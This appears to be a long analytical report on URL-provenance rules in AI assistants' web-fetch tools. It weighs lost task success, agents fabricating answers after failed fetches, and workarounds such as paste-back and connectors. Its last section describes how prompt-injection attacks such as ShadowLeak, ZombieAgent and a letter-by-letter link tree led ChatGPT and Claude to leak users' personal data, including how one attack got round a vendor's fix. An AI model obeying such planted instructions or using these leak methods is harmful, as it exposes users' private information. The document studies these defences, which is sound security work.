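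Shah found that the agents' accuracy stayed in the mid-to-high 90s in every format, but that result doesn't carry over to Claude chat. The agents eventually found the right page because they could keep trying addresses and follow any links they came across, and the chat app's rule forbids both.

An index can still be useful when Claude can't open its links. Of the 329 runs in Vercel's study in which an agent reached an llms.txt file, 36% ended with an answer drawn from the file itself. The agent later opened a page that the file listed in 36% of runs, possibly including some of the same ones. So the short descriptions sometimes answer the question, and an assistant could use the titles as search terms. But Claude has to reach the index first. In Vercel's data, agents followed a link to llms.txt in 86% of fetches and guessed the address in the other 14%. Claude chat can do neither, so it depends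 on the user or a search to supply the address.

These failures may matter less to programmers than one would expect. *From Agent Behaviour to Agent-Friendly Documentation* (2026) examined 557 sessions with coding agents and 33,097 code changes submitted by agents. API reference pages made up only 1.3% of the agents' interactions with documentation, while instruction files and working notes, which agents also write themselves, made up 60.5%. Agents turned to documentation first in 5.4% of the 2,034 cases where something went wrong. These figures don't show how useful a rare lookup is, and a chat user who asks how to install a program has different needs from an agent in a coding session. But they make it unlikely that guessing documentation addresses is a large part of what coding agents do.

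### How many of the guesses would have worked?

Models also make up addresses, which is a reason to refuse constructed URLs even when no private data is at risk. If most guessed addresses don't lead to a real page, the rule mainly prevents wasted requests.

*How Often Do AI Assistants Hallucinate Links?* (Law, 2025), the largest count, covers 16 million URLs that six AI assistants gave to users. It found that 2.38% of the URLs ChatGPT cited returned a 404, the code for a missing page, compared with 0.84% of top Google results. The invented addresses tended to look right. For example, visitors to the blog of Ahrefs, the marketing software company where Law works, often arrived looking for `/blog/internal-links/`, which doesn't exist, although the blog covers that kind of subject. SE Ranking's undated *ChatGPT is twice as likely to lead users to broken links* reports a similar result, with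 1.22% for ChatGPT and 0.65% for ordinary Google results.

*Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents* (Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch, 2026) reports higher rates than Law's. Rao and colleagues tested ten models and research agents, most from 2025, and 5–18% of the cited URLs failed to load. Some of those pages had gone offline. To separate these from invented addresses, the researchers looked up each dead URL in the Wayback Machine, an archive of old web pages, and found no record of 3–13% of all the cited URLs. Part of the gap with Law's figures probably arises because Law could check only addresses already in Ahrefs's crawler database, which leaves out many that never existed.

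None of these rates measures guessing very well, because an assistant with a search tool can copy most of its citations from the results. *BaRA* (Lee, Lee and colleagues, 2026) measures it better. In one test, Gemini 3 Flash proposed pages on 50 real websites without browsing them, and 25% of the addresses worked. When agents using the same model browsed those sites, 94–98% of the addresses they returned worked. Lee and colleagues also built 50 artificial sites, which the model can't have seen in training, and only 13% of the addresses it proposed there without browsing worked.

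Even 25% may be too generous, because some sites return a page for any address at all. Zhang (2026), in *When 200 OK Is Not an Answer*, requested random, non-existent addresses on about 1,500 sites in October 2026. Of the sites that answered, 13.1% returned 200, the code for success. If wrong guesses on Lee and colleagues' real sites passed their test at that rate, only about 14% of the guesses reached a page that existed:

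0.14 + 0.86 × 0.131 ≈ 0.25

This is a rough, pessimistic estimate that combines two samples. The responses can be misleading as well as useless. An automated labeller in Zhang's study mistook 28 of 172 such responses for real content, often because the site served its homepage or a general listing. An assistant could make the same mistake and answer from the wrong page.

Links from an index work much more often than guessed addresses. Zhang also tested pages listed in llms.txt files, and 91% returned a 200 status. About nine in ten of those responses contained the page's main content. The sample favoured links that had worked before, but that can't explain the whole difference from the 25% for guessed addresses.

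For the small edits in this section, though, 25% is surely far too low. Lee and colleagues used mostly obscure sites, and the model had to produce the addresses from memory. If the first page of a list says "1 of 12", `page=2` will almost certainly work, and so will `sort=newest` if the site's own menu offers that order. Adding `.md` works on sites that follow Howard's convention and usually fails elsewhere. Swapping a version number fails when the developers have moved or renamed the page. None of these studies measured such edits separately, so this ranking is a judgement. On that judgement, the risk that a model will invent an address is a good reason to distrust addresses it recalls, but a weak reason to refuse page two.

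An assistant that makes a small edit to a URL, such as changing the page number, stays on the site it was already reading, so it also avoids a danger of writing whole addresses from memory. *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain* (2025) warns that models writing code sometimes refer to domains or GitHub accounts that don't exist. An attacker can register the missing name and put malicious files there.

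An assistant can also catch a wrong guess easily if it can test the address. Rao and colleagues gave three models a tool that reports whether a URL loads. The share of dead addresses in the answers fell from 16.0% to 0.6% for GPT-5.1, and from 4.9% to 0.8% for Claude Sonnet 4.5. A smaller model, GPT-5 nano, did worse because it kept proposing addresses that the tool had already flagged. But testing an address means requesting it, which Anthropic's rule prevents. Claude gets the same error for `page=2` of a list it has just read as for a page that never existed, so it can't tell from the error whether a guessed address exists.

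## What does the assistant do after a refusal, and how large is the measured loss?

No published study measures how many tasks fail because an assistant can't open the URLs it writes. The evidence is better on what assistants do when a tool of any kind fails. It suggests that they mostly answer honestly after a clear refusal, and are more likely to make something up when they get only part of what they needed.

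### One refused request

Suppose the user who asked about earthquakes above magnitude 5 during six weeks of spring 2019 only wants to know how many there were. Claude writes the `count` version of the USGS query and passes it to the fetch tool. The tool returns the error `url_not_in_prior_context` without sending anything to USGS.

The sample error in Anthropic's documentation contains a type and a code, with no explanation or suggested next step. The API request still succeeds, returning status code 200 with the error inside the response, so a developer who monitors only status codes would miss the refusal. Claude reads the error and continues its turn.

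Claude can use the error code to decide what to do next. After `url_not_allowed`, which covers blocked domains and robots.txt restrictions, trying another site is usually best. After `url_not_in_prior_context`, the user may be able to solve the problem by sending the address. Claude still doesn't know whether USGS would have accepted the query.

The tool can return the same code even when Claude hasn't changed the URL. One test in *Fetch, Read, Reuse* (Chen, Canini and colleagues, 2026), a study of how AI services fetch web pages, added `:443` to the host in a URL. That is the default port for `https`, so adding it doesn't change which page the URL leads to. Claude copied the URL exactly from the user's message, but the tool refused it in all three trials. Perhaps the tool removes the port from only one of the two URLs, the user's or Claude's, before comparing them.

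The error code is more confusing in Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running longer tasks. Anthropic tightened the fetch rule there on 7 October 2026, so the agent can no longer fetch a URL that appears only in an attached document, the system prompt, or the output of a tool such as `bash`. If a user attaches a report and asks the agent to check its sources, the agent can read the links but can't open them. The error reads as if the links were missing from the conversation, although the agent has just read them. Anthropic's remedy is to put the URL in the text of a user message, which the agent can't do itself.

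### What Claude can do next

Claude gains nothing by trying the same URL again until someone else supplies it. In the earthquake example it has five other options:

- It can ask the user to send the URL. This works only if someone is there to reply, which is unlikely for an agent that runs overnight.
- It can search for a page that gives the number. Such a page probably exists for the whole of 2019, but not for these six weeks.
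- It can answer from a snippet, the short extract that a search engine shows under each result. A snippet may leave out the dates or the magnitude that a figure refers to.
- It can answer from memory.
- It can say that it couldn't get the number.

Memory isn't useless here. The world has roughly 1,500 earthquakes of this size in a typical year, and the period lasts 46 days, so Claude could estimate:

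1,500 × 46 / 365 ≈ 189

This is a reasonable answer if Claude calls it an estimate. If Claude writes that the USGS catalogue lists 189 earthquakes, it has invented a measurement, and the user may copy the figure into a report and cite USGS.

The invented count is worse than no answer because the user has no reason to check it. If Claude says it couldn't reach the catalogue, the user can open the URL in a browser and get the number within a minute. *When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate* (2026) makes the same distinction between a "loud, honest failure", from which people or software can recover later, and a silent fabrication. The distinction matters even more when an agent uses the number in its next calculation, because nobody may look at the original claim.

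Memory is also least reliable for the questions that most need a fetch, such as those about recent events or obscure records. Some answers from memory will be right, but the user can't tell which if Claude presents them all as things it has read.

Failed attempts also cost money. Chen and colleagues found that for a small page, a failed fetch used about as many input tokens (the pieces of text providers charge for) as a successful one. Those fetches failed at the website. A refusal that never reaches the site may cost less, but Claude still has to read the error and decide what to do.

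### How often do assistants hide a failure?

*Fabrication After Tool Failure* (2026) examined what agents do when a tool doesn't return a value they need. In 10–25% of cases, depending on the prompt, the agents stated a value anyway or invented a reason for withholding one. The rate depended almost entirely on whether the tool's response marked the call as failed. When it did, the agents reported the failure honestly, and most of the fabrication came from cases where they had to infer the failure themselves.

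None of the nine production prompts in the study's audit specified what an agent should do after a failed call. Adding one sentence that named a failure state cut dishonest answers about tenfold.

*When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate* also found that the type of fault affected the outcome more than the choice of model did. Agents fabricated answers in up to 38% of cases when a tool returned partial data, but mostly admitted failure after an outright denial.

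*Failure-Transparent Agents* (2026) introduces a benchmark of tasks that the agent cannot complete, and finds that an agent may claim success even after a visible error. Agents made far fewer unsupported claims under a policy that required them to report their evidence in a fixed structure, and their answers mostly remained useful.

A provenance refusal denies the fetch outright and returns an explicit error, so on this evidence Claude should usually admit it. But none of the three studies gives a rate for this error, and I expect more trouble from fetches that succeed.

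In the library search described earlier, Claude can read 20 of 240 books about bridges. If it tries page two, it gets an error that it can report. If it knows the rule and doesn't try, it has partial data and no error, which is close to the condition that produced the most fabrication. It may then tell the user that the library has no book about the Forth Bridge. A search snippet creates the same risk, because it looks like an answer but leaves out most of the page.

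The error message also affects what the user learns. Chen and colleagues asked several services to quote the first lines of 299 public files. OpenAI's model refused 225 times, and in 192 of those answers it quoted its fetch tool's error, such as an unsupported content type. Google's model refused 151 times and never gave a reason, because its tool's error doesn't contain one. The prompt told the models to say plainly if they couldn't read a file, so this test can't show how often they would have hidden a failure without that instruction.

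### Failures without an error

Some fetches fail but look successful. In *Continuing without info from webpage*, a 2026 bug report about the code editor Cursor, a user gave the assistant a link to a ChatGPT conversation and asked it to use the code there. The fetch tool got an almost empty page because the conversation loads through JavaScript. The assistant didn't mention this and went on building the solution the user was trying to replace. Someone replied that the assistant's silence was "the real bug" and that the JavaScript problem was a known limitation.

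To measure how common such pages are, Zhang fetched 7,293 pages with a simple client that doesn't run JavaScript. Of the 60.2% that returned a status of 200, 20.9% lacked the page's main content, according to an automated labeller. In those cases the client had received an empty frame, a bot check, an error page or only part of the text. A review of 300 responses suggested the labeller was somewhat too strict, but the share stayed near one in five.

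These failures can distort later work. Zhang also checked whether cited web pages still supported the claims attached to them. When Zhang treated every 200 response as the real page, 21.9% of the sources that had once supported a claim no longer seemed to. After Zhang removed the unusable responses, the figure was 5.8%. An assistant that checks references could make the same mistake, reporting that a source doesn't support a claim when it has only read a bot check.

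Zhang tested fetches but not the answers that agents write afterwards. Some assistants do notice missing content. Agent Ecosystem Testing's *Key Findings for Claude's Web Fetch Tool, Claude-interpreted* describes a tutorial page that arrived without its code examples, and Claude correctly explained that they needed JavaScript. But the tester had asked Claude to describe what it received, which few users do. Claude also put the length of another page at about 14,000 characters, while the script measured 25,925.

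Reading a long page can fail silently as well. Chen and colleagues found that xAI's tool reads only the first half megabyte of a page, without notifying the user. An honest error report can also be out of date. After they repaired a page that had returned an error, Claude kept reporting it as broken for as long as they tested, up to about 11 hours, without requesting it again.

The provenance rule doesn't cause these failures, but it can make them more likely to matter, because the assistant depends more on what a search finds. Fetch tools could help by labelling bad pages as failures. In Zhang's test, a few simple checks, such as whether the text is very short or the site has redirected to its homepage, caught 86% of unusable responses and wrongly flagged about 6% of usable ones.

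### The missing measurement

The loss in task success depends on two numbers: how many tasks lead the assistant to a URL that the rule refuses, and how much less often those tasks succeed as a result. If 10% of tasks involve such a URL, and the refusal lowers their success rate from 80% to 50%, the overall loss is:

0.10 × (0.80 − 0.50) = 0.03, or 3 percentage points

These figures are made up because neither has a published value. The example shows that the average loss can be small even when the loss is large for people who often query databases.

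*WebNavigator* (2026) lists the actions available in five web agent systems. WebArena, BrowserGym and SteP include `goto(URL)`, which opens any address the agent writes, while AgentOccam and WebNavigator don't. Differences in their benchmark scores can't be attributed to `goto`, because the systems also differ in many other ways. For example, SteP has 27 actions, including special ones for finding a customer or an order, and AgentOccam has eight.

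These agents also control a browser, so without `goto` they can still click "next" or fill in a search form. They therefore lose much less than an assistant that has only a fetch tool. WebNavigator instead jumps to pages from a stored graph of the site. In at most 9.1% of cases, it found no suitable page and continued from the current one. This suggests that a good list of known pages can replace many of the URLs an agent would otherwise write itself, at least on sites that someone has mapped in advance.

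Logs that sort requests by where the URL came from would supply the first number. The closest figure is Vercel's count of guessed llms.txt addresses, but it covers only one unusually predictable address. Mintlify's experiment measured how often agents guess URLs, but not what happens when a rule stops them.

Neither Anthropic nor OpenAI seems to have published a refusal rate. Chen and colleagues report that Anthropic's tool refused to fetch 19% of the plain-text files and 14–19% of the XML files. But the prompts contained the URLs, and Claude's answers gave the site's domain as the reason, so these refusals aren't evidence about constructed URLs. They do show that user-supplied URLs often fail too.

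In the same study, Chen and colleagues gave every test page a new address, which no independent crawler could have recorded beforehand. OpenAI's tool still downloaded the pages, both through the API and in ChatGPT, despite the company's public-index check. The check may exempt addresses that the user types, or the researchers may have accepted a warning that they didn't record. Either way, OpenAI's published description isn't enough to estimate how often the check blocks a request.

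### How to measure the loss

A convincing study would start with real sessions in which the agent could open any URL. Logs from a restricted tool would undercount the problem, because a model that knows the rule may never try the address it needs. Researchers could then proceed as follows:

1. They label each requested URL by origin: typed by the user, returned by search, linked in a fetched page, printed by another tool, edited by the assistant, or written from nothing. They also need a policy for trivial differences such as `:443`.
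2. They find the first URL in each session that a given rule would refuse, return the real error code at that point, and let the agent continue from there.
3. They repeat this for the Claude API's rule, the chat app's reported rule and a public-index check, and rerun the session with free access as a control.
4. They compare task success, extra turns, cost and unsupported answers.

After a refusal, the agent may search for something else or ask the user a question. The old log has no responses to those steps, so the agent has to run again from the refusal onward. The reruns should take place close together because web pages change, and each session needs several because the same model can succeed once and fail the next time. Some runs should include a simulated user who sends a URL when asked, and others should have nobody to ask. Outsiders can't query OpenAI's index, so they would have to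 approximate it with a public crawl.

The sample must be fairly large. Suppose the rule turns success into failure in 5% of sessions, while chance produces the opposite change in 2%. The net loss is 3 points. To measure it to within 1 point at 95% confidence, with one run under each condition, researchers would need about this many sessions:

1.96² × (0.05 + 0.02 − 0.03²) / 0.01² ≈ 2,650

Rerunning only the sessions that contain a refused URL would save work, since the rule can't affect the others unless the model knows about it in advance.

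In *When Tools Fail, Agents Fabricate*, two AI judges sorted the agents' behaviour into categories and reached an agreement of only 0.58, where 1 is perfect and 0 is chance. Their agreement rose to 0.91 when they compared answers with the known truth. The tasks should therefore have answers that researchers can check. Researchers should also check separately whether the agent read its evidence, because a lucky answer from memory would otherwise count as a full success.

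The control runs will also fail on some pages. In Zhang's sample, the simple client obtained the main content of only about 48% of pages (0.602 × 0.791), partly because many came from old citations. Blaming the provenance rule for every page Claude failed to read would greatly overstate the loss.

Anthropic may already have the data for a rougher version. Managed Agents could apparently open constructed URLs until 7 October 2026, so the company could compare recurring jobs before and after that date. Anthropic also began applying host restrictions to the fetch tool in certain environments that day, and added organisation-wide domain limits on 20 October, so the comparison would have to exclude agents affected by either change. Jobs that kept the same model throughout would give the cleanest result.

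## How do users and developers get the work done anyway?

Nobody has measured the loss, but developers who ran into it have written instructions for dealing with it. These are more informative than their complaints, which are few and mostly concern a different check.

### Reactions to the rule

Some developers just pass the rule on to their users. The manual for ellmer, an R package for using language models, restates it in two sentences and refers readers to Anthropic.

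When the tool came out, Willison first thought it might open only URLs from the user's own prompts, and he was disappointed that it also accepted URLs from the output of other tools. He still considered the ban on URLs that Claude generates the most protective part of the design. In July 2026, he reported the hole that Paul had found in the design, but wrote that the design had impressed him. Willison writes about security, though, and a user who only wants the second page of library search results may be less pleased.

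The angriest posts are about connectors, which link an assistant to an outside service through functions that the service defines, such as one for finding flights. In *ChatGPT App MCP tool calls blocked by OpenAI safety checks*, a thread on OpenAI's forum, a developer reported that ChatGPT had blocked a search for one-way flights from Frankfurt or Düsseldorf to Ibiza or Palma. The function could not book or change anything, and the request never reached the developer's server. About a dozen replies described similar blocks, including one from a developer whose app had worked for months and whose users were now complaining. Someone apparently from OpenAI later acknowledged the problem and said the company was working on it. In another thread, *Approved ChatGPT app's tool calls getting blocked*, a developer guessed that the cause was a function that accepted URLs, but nobody confirmed this.

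People post on such forums when something breaks, so a few threads can't show what share of requests fail. The threads also reveal little about ordinary users, who may never learn why an answer was incomplete.

### How Base ranks the alternatives

Base, the blockchain network whose guide came up earlier, gives unusually detailed instructions for working within the rule. Its Base MCP connector lets an assistant use a person's cryptocurrency wallet through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way for assistants to call functions on other servers. A plugin is a Markdown file with instructions for using one more financial service through that wallet.

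Suppose a user asks Claude to deposit 25 dollars' worth of a currency with a lending service. Claude gets the wallet's address from Base MCP and asks the lender's API to prepare the transaction. It then hands the result to Base MCP, and the user approves the transaction. For the request to the lender, Claude needs a URL like this one, with the full wallet address in place of the dots:

`https://api.lender.example/prepare/deposit?from=0x52...&amount=25`

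A search engine is very unlikely to have a URL that combines this user's wallet with this amount, so Claude has to construct it. Base tells the agent to try three routes in order:

1. If the agent runs in a program with its own network access, such as Claude Code, Codex or the code editor Cursor, it sends the request from there.
2. Otherwise it uses `web_request`, a function of Base MCP that sends the request from Base's server, but only to hosts on Base's allowlist.
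3. If the host isn't on that list, the agent writes out the full URL and asks the user to paste it into the chat. This is paste-back, and it works only for GET requests.

Paste-back is mainly for plugins that users write themselves, because Base's list almost certainly omits those plugins' hosts. Of the seven plugins that Base maintains, three work through ordinary APIs, whose hosts should be on the list, and a fourth has its own MCP server, according to Base's specification. An earlier edition of Base's guide describes the other three. In a chat app, Morpho also works through an MCP server. Avantis lets the agent look up prices and positions through `web_request`, but the agent has to send the user to the Avantis website to trade. Aerodrome needs a command line, so the agent should explain this and stop.

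Base says that Claude and ChatGPT both fetch only URLs the user has pasted. This is too narrow for Claude, which also opens search results, and it differs more seriously from OpenAI's account of ChatGPT. According to that account, ChatGPT would not find the lender's URL in its public index, so it would either block the request or show the user what it would send and ask for confirmation. If it asks, the user doesn't need to paste anything.

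Base's third route probably does work in ChatGPT, though, since it opened the brand-new addresses in Chen and colleagues' prompts.

Base's ranking leaves out site-restricted search and a developer's own tool that returns URLs. The table compares all six routes on three of the earlier tasks.

| Route | Counting earthquakes | Pages 2 to 12 of a library list | Search form that uses POST | What someone has to do first |
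|---|---|---|---|---|
| Paste-back | Yes | Yes | No | Copy the URLs into the chat |
| Search restricted to one site | Rarely | Rarely | No | Nothing |
| Connector | If it has a suitable function | If it has a suitable function | If it has a suitable function | Build and install it |
| Developer's tool that returns URLs | Yes | Yes | Only if the tool runs the search itself | Write the tool |
| Domain allowlist | Yes, in products where it permits constructed URLs | Yes, in the same products | Not with a tool that takes only a URL | Add the site to the list |
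| Coding agent | Yes | Yes | Yes | Install it and give it network access |

### Paste-back

Paste-back works because Claude's fetch tool accepts any address in a user message, no matter who wrote it first. In the earthquake example, Claude writes the `count` URL, the user copies it into the chat, and Claude can then request the number from USGS. The same method works for a filtered library search or the version 5 installation page.

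Claude can write the URLs for the remaining eleven pages of the library's list all at once, and the user can paste them in a single message. With an API that returns bare cursors, the user has to paste eleven times, because each cursor comes with the previous page.

Pasting has a longer history in these apps. In 2024 Claude couldn't open links, and its system prompt told it to ask people for the text itself (Willison, 2024). Willison reported that Alex Albert of Anthropic announced in May 2025 that Claude would fetch a link users dropped into any chat. Mistral's documentation describes pasting a link as the usual way to have its assistant, Le Chat, read a known page. Le Chat fetches only that page, not the rest of the site. Base adds to this by having the assistant write the link that the user pastes.

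Paste-back works only with GET, so Base's *Custom Plugins* advises services to offer GET requests if they want to reach people in the chat apps. But this puts the user's details in the URL, which websites commonly log.

URL length can also be a problem. A wallet address on Base has 42 characters, so a request that names one wallet and two currencies by their addresses uses 126 of the 250 characters the Claude API allows, before adding a host or an amount.

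The answer may be out of date too, because Anthropic's tool keeps copies of pages it has fetched. Classmethod's *Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* describes a developer who asked about limits in the messaging app Slack. Claude kept giving 101 rows and 10,000 characters, although Slack's documentation listed 201 and 20,000. The developer thought the cache was the most likely cause. Fetching a URL with a new combination of parameters should avoid this problem, but checking the same price or account balance again may return the old figure. The API has an option to bypass the cache, but this doesn't help someone using the chat app.

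Base also suggests a variant in which the user pastes the API's response instead of its URL. The user can open the URL in a browser and copy the result. This works for long URLs, JSON, and pages that need the user's login, all of which can make Claude's fetch tool fail. But a list of several hundred earthquakes makes a very long message. Any text an attacker has planted in the response also reaches Claude as part of a user message, and on the API any links in that text count as user-supplied.

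### Does the user read the address?

Paste-back puts a person between a hijacked assistant and the network. An attacker can no longer get the data silently, because the user has to copy the address that contains it. The protection depends on how carefully the user checks the address, though, and some addresses are almost impossible to read.

In the hotel example, Mara Lind would probably recognise her own email address in `mara.lind%40post.example`. In Base64, a common way to write data as letters and digits, the same address becomes:

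`bWFyYS5saW5kQHBvc3QuZXhhbXBsZQ==`

Many harmless URLs contain strings like this, including pagination cursors for long lists. A user who has just pasted three such URLs has little reason to be suspicious of the fourth.

Research on phishing suggests that people rarely look closely at a link's address. In the experiment in *Eyes on the Phish(er)* (2024), participants hovered over a phishing email's link to check its real address in only two cases, and in both they reported the email. Most saw the real address only in the browser, after clicking. Even then, many fell for hosts such as `docs-google.online`.

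Users may trust an address that their own assistant gives them to paste back more than a phishing link in a strange email, which could make them easier to deceive. But they also know what they asked for, so if they requested USGS data, an unfamiliar host should stand out.

Repeated permission prompts probably make people less careful. Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. Anthropic points out that most of these are probably for safe commands, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness.

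The developer site Hyrax reports more direct evidence from a test by Anthropic, in which people stopped only 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands (13.6%). The rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic had already described the problem as approval fatigue in *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, and OpenAI also worries that frequent warnings train people to click through them.

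If users caught bad addresses as rarely as those testers caught bad commands, paste-back would stop about one leak in seven. They may do better, because copying a URL takes more effort than pressing "approve", but they can still copy it without reading it. *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) included a task in which participants had to drag the parts of a URL into place before they could visit the page, and paste-back has no comparable step. Users are especially unlikely to look carefully at eleven similar URLs in one block.

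The host is the most important part of the URL to check because, unless the site redirects the request, everything in the URL goes to whoever runs that host. A query to `earthquake.usgs.gov` therefore can't send Mara's email address to a stranger's server. In Base's case, the user also has to approve the transaction, but only after the lender's server has received everything in the URL.

### Searching a single site

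An assistant can restrict a web search to one site, often by adding an operator such as `site:docs.example` to the search terms. Developers can sometimes set the permitted domains in the search tool instead, as jupyterlite-ai does in its sample settings for OpenAI's models. Claude may then open any of the results, because their URLs came from a search.

ChatGPT may already use the `site:` operator routinely. Security Arsenal's *ChatGPT Search Now Uses the site* (2026) reports large-scale use since the GPT-5 models appeared, citing figures from Promptwatch, which tracks chatbots' answers for marketing purposes. The evidence is thin because Security Arsenal is a security vendor summarising another company's data.

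Restricted search is best at finding one known page, such as chapter four of a manual or the installation guide for version 5. It is free and needs no setup. It can't count earthquakes or apply a court database's filters, and it often returns few results. For instance, when an organisation connects its own search server to Claude Desktop, Anthropic uses at most ten results per search and cuts each snippet to 600 characters. In the library example, one search would return at most ten of the 240 books.

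The search provider sees any private details in the search terms, but an attacker who has only planted text on a web page doesn't. The results are more dangerous. Security Arsenal warns that someone can plant instructions in a forum post or comment on the chosen site, and that users may trust the answer more because it seems to come from that site.

### Connectors

A connector lets the assistant fill in fields instead of writing a URL. An earthquake connector might offer a function called `count_earthquakes` with fields for the first day, the last day and the smallest magnitude. Claude supplies the values, and the connector's server builds the request and sends it to USGS. That server can use POST, add an access key, read JSON and work through a series of cursors, which Claude's fetch tool may not be able to do. OpenAI, which calls its connectors apps, says they retrieve data from the source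 when the user needs it and pass the relevant parts to the model.

Someone has to build and maintain a connector for each service. That is worthwhile for a popular travel company, but a county court with a few visitors a month is unlikely to have one.

ChatGPT may also block calls to a connector. In the forum thread about the blocked flight search, one developer reported that functions without parameters ran normally, but ChatGPT sometimes blocked those with parameters. Another developer sent the same file-read request several times, and ChatGPT blocked only some of the attempts. Parameters could carry private data out of the conversation, so an overly sensitive leak check would explain the first pattern. It wouldn't explain why an identical request failed only some of the time, and the reply in the thread gave no cause.

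Some connectors depend on an allowlist as well. Some functions in the connector from Common Paper, a contract software company, require the assistant to run a separate command, for example to upload a file. The company tells customers to add its host to the allowlist in ChatGPT, Codex or Claude, because otherwise the assistant can't run those commands even with the connector attached.

A connector's operator receives whatever the assistant puts in the fields. A planted instruction could therefore make the assistant put private text in a search field, though the text would at least go to a service the user had chosen.

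Connectors that run on the user's computer carry a different risk. Base describes installing one as "arbitrary code execution on the user's machine" and requires plugin authors to name an exact version of the program. If a plugin were set to always fetch the latest version, the program's author could send new code to every user without review. Local connectors can't run in the Claude or ChatGPT chat apps, and Base tells the agent to say so instead of improvising a substitute.

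### A developer's own tool

The Claude API accepts URLs from client-side tools, so developers can write a function that returns URLs for Claude to open. For the earthquake catalogue, the function could accept two dates and a magnitude, check that each is valid, and return a complete USGS URL. A similar function for the library could return the URLs of pages 2 to 12.

This keeps most of the protection if the fields are narrow. The developer's code fixes the host, and an email address won't fit into a date field. A hijacked assistant could still hide a message in its choice of dates and magnitude, but not a long one. The earlier count found about 67 million combinations over ten years, which can carry slightly less than 26 bits of information:

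log₂(66,630,750) ≈ 25.99

That isn't quite enough to spell an arbitrary six-letter name, and the request would go to USGS. Repeated requests could carry more information, and a free-text field in the function would remove most of this protection.

The developer has to write and maintain this code for each site, and chat app users can't add it themselves. It also may not work in Managed Agents, where Anthropic stopped accepting URLs from the output of tools such as `bash` in October 2026.

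Developers can also supply their own fetch tool. The jupyterlite-ai project instructs its assistant to try the project's browser-based tool before Anthropic's when fetching a specific URL. Browsers often stop a program on one site from reading a page on another, so the tool can't read every public page. This restriction does little to prevent leaks, because a browser will usually send a simple GET request even if it then withholds the response from the program.

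Organisations that use Claude Desktop through another provider can have their own MCP server handle every fetch. Claude passes the server an address and gets the page back as text, so the server could apply any rule the organisation likes, including one that permits `page=2`. The organisation's allowlist doesn't limit these fetches. The server's own settings determine which hosts it contacts, including private addresses inside the company's network, so a careless setup could expose internal pages to a hijacked assistant.

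### Adding a site to an allowlist

Some allowlists let an assistant construct URLs for the sites they contain, which restores nearly every GET task on those sites. For example, if an administrator adds `earthquake.usgs.gov` to the list in that version of Claude Desktop, Claude can write any query to that site. Adding the site to a list on the Claude API doesn't have this effect, because the list there only restricts which URLs Claude may open.

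The administrator has to know in advance which sites people will need. This suits a team that uses the same five databases every day, but not a user who asks which small museums have a certain kind of clock.

Products also interpret entries differently. On the Claude API, `example.com` also covers `docs.example.com`. In Claude Desktop and Docker's fetch tool for agents, `*.example.com` covers the subdomains but not `example.com` itself. An administrator who copies a list from one product to another could therefore permit too much or too little. Anthropic also warns about lookalike letters, such as a Cyrillic "а" in what appears to be `amazon.com`.

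Switching models can remove the domain list. Posit, which makes data analysis tools, offers a fetch function that works with both Claude and Gemini, but its domain settings work only with Claude.

The main security risk comes from permitted sites where anyone can open an account. Willison reported that researchers extracted files from Cowork through one such site in January 2026. Anthropic now warns administrators that commands the agent runs can reach these sites with any account's credentials. In September 2025, Willison had already called finding domains that nobody can use to extract data "a tricky proposition".

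### Moving to a coding agent

Base prefers an agent with its own network access because it can send any type of request to any host and gets the full response. The agent can also write a short program. For the library, the program could go through all twelve pages and save every record. For the earthquakes, it could download the catalogue as JSON and count the events deeper than 50 kilometres, so the answer wouldn't depend on a smaller model's reading of a web page.

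The user needs to install the agent or set up its environment, and be comfortable with a tool made for programmers. They may also have to turn on the agent's internet access, which is the first step in Common Paper's instructions for ChatGPT and Codex.

This route brings back most of the original risk. *Takedown* (2025) concluded that a fetch tool that works without the user's approval leads directly to data leaks, and it found one coding agent with such a tool. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested an agent that automatically previewed URLs, and planted text caused the agent to send unintended requests about 89% of the time. A safety check that looked only at the agent's reply missed 95% of the successful attacks. The tests used a custom local setup, so the rates won't carry over exactly to Claude Code or Codex.

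Asking users to approve each request would help, but they can approve by habit here too, and some agents no longer ask. In the version of Claude Desktop for other providers, new coding sessions start in auto mode, which fetches pages without asking, even from sites not on the organisation's allowlist. Administrators can require approval for every fetch. They can also confine the agent's commands to listed hosts, but this needs a sandbox that doesn't run on Windows, where those commands can reach any host the company's network permits.

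## How much data theft does the rule prevent?

Refusing constructed URLs stops an assistant from sending a paragraph of private text in a single request. It protects a name or a six-digit code much less, because the assistant can still reveal those by choosing which existing URL to open. Neither Anthropic nor OpenAI seems to have published how many thefts its rule has blocked, so the evidence comes from leaks that researchers found, calculations of how much data a request can carry, and laboratory tests of related defences.

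### Three leaks and their fixes

Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025) describes a simple case of this theft. An attacker hid instructions in an email to someone whose ChatGPT account was connected to Gmail. When that person asked ChatGPT to summarise the inbox, it collected names, addresses and other details from recent emails, then requested a URL on the attacker's site with those details as parameters. The attack worked about half the time with a simple instruction, and considerably more often once Radware made the request look urgent and official. OpenAI's servers sent the request, so it left no trace on the network of the victim's employer.

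OpenAI responded by forbidding ChatGPT to alter URLs. Radware published ShadowLeak on 18 September 2025, and eight days later it reported a way around the new rule, which it named ZombieAgent. The attacker supplied a set of finished URLs, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. ChatGPT could then send a name to the attacker's log by opening the matching URLs in order, without writing or changing any address. By 29 September, Radware had a version that worked every time. OpenAI fixed the problem eleven weeks later. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT stopped opening links that came from an email unless they were in a well-known public index.

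In July 2026, Ayush Paul found a similar way to steal data through Claude's chat app. Claude refused to put Paul's name into a URL, but it still followed links in pages it had fetched. Paul built a site whose homepage linked to one page for each letter. The page for "a" linked to "aa", "ab" and so on, and the server created each page when Claude requested it. Claude spelled out Paul's full name one link at a time. Paul then disguised the site as a coffee shop with a security check, and obtained the user's name, employer and hometown while the visible conversation looked normal. The site showed the trap only to Claude, so a person who opened the same link would have noticed nothing.

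Anthropic stopped the chat app from following links, so users could no longer do the multi-page tasks described earlier. It did not pay Paul a bounty because, according to Willison, it said it had already found the problem internally.

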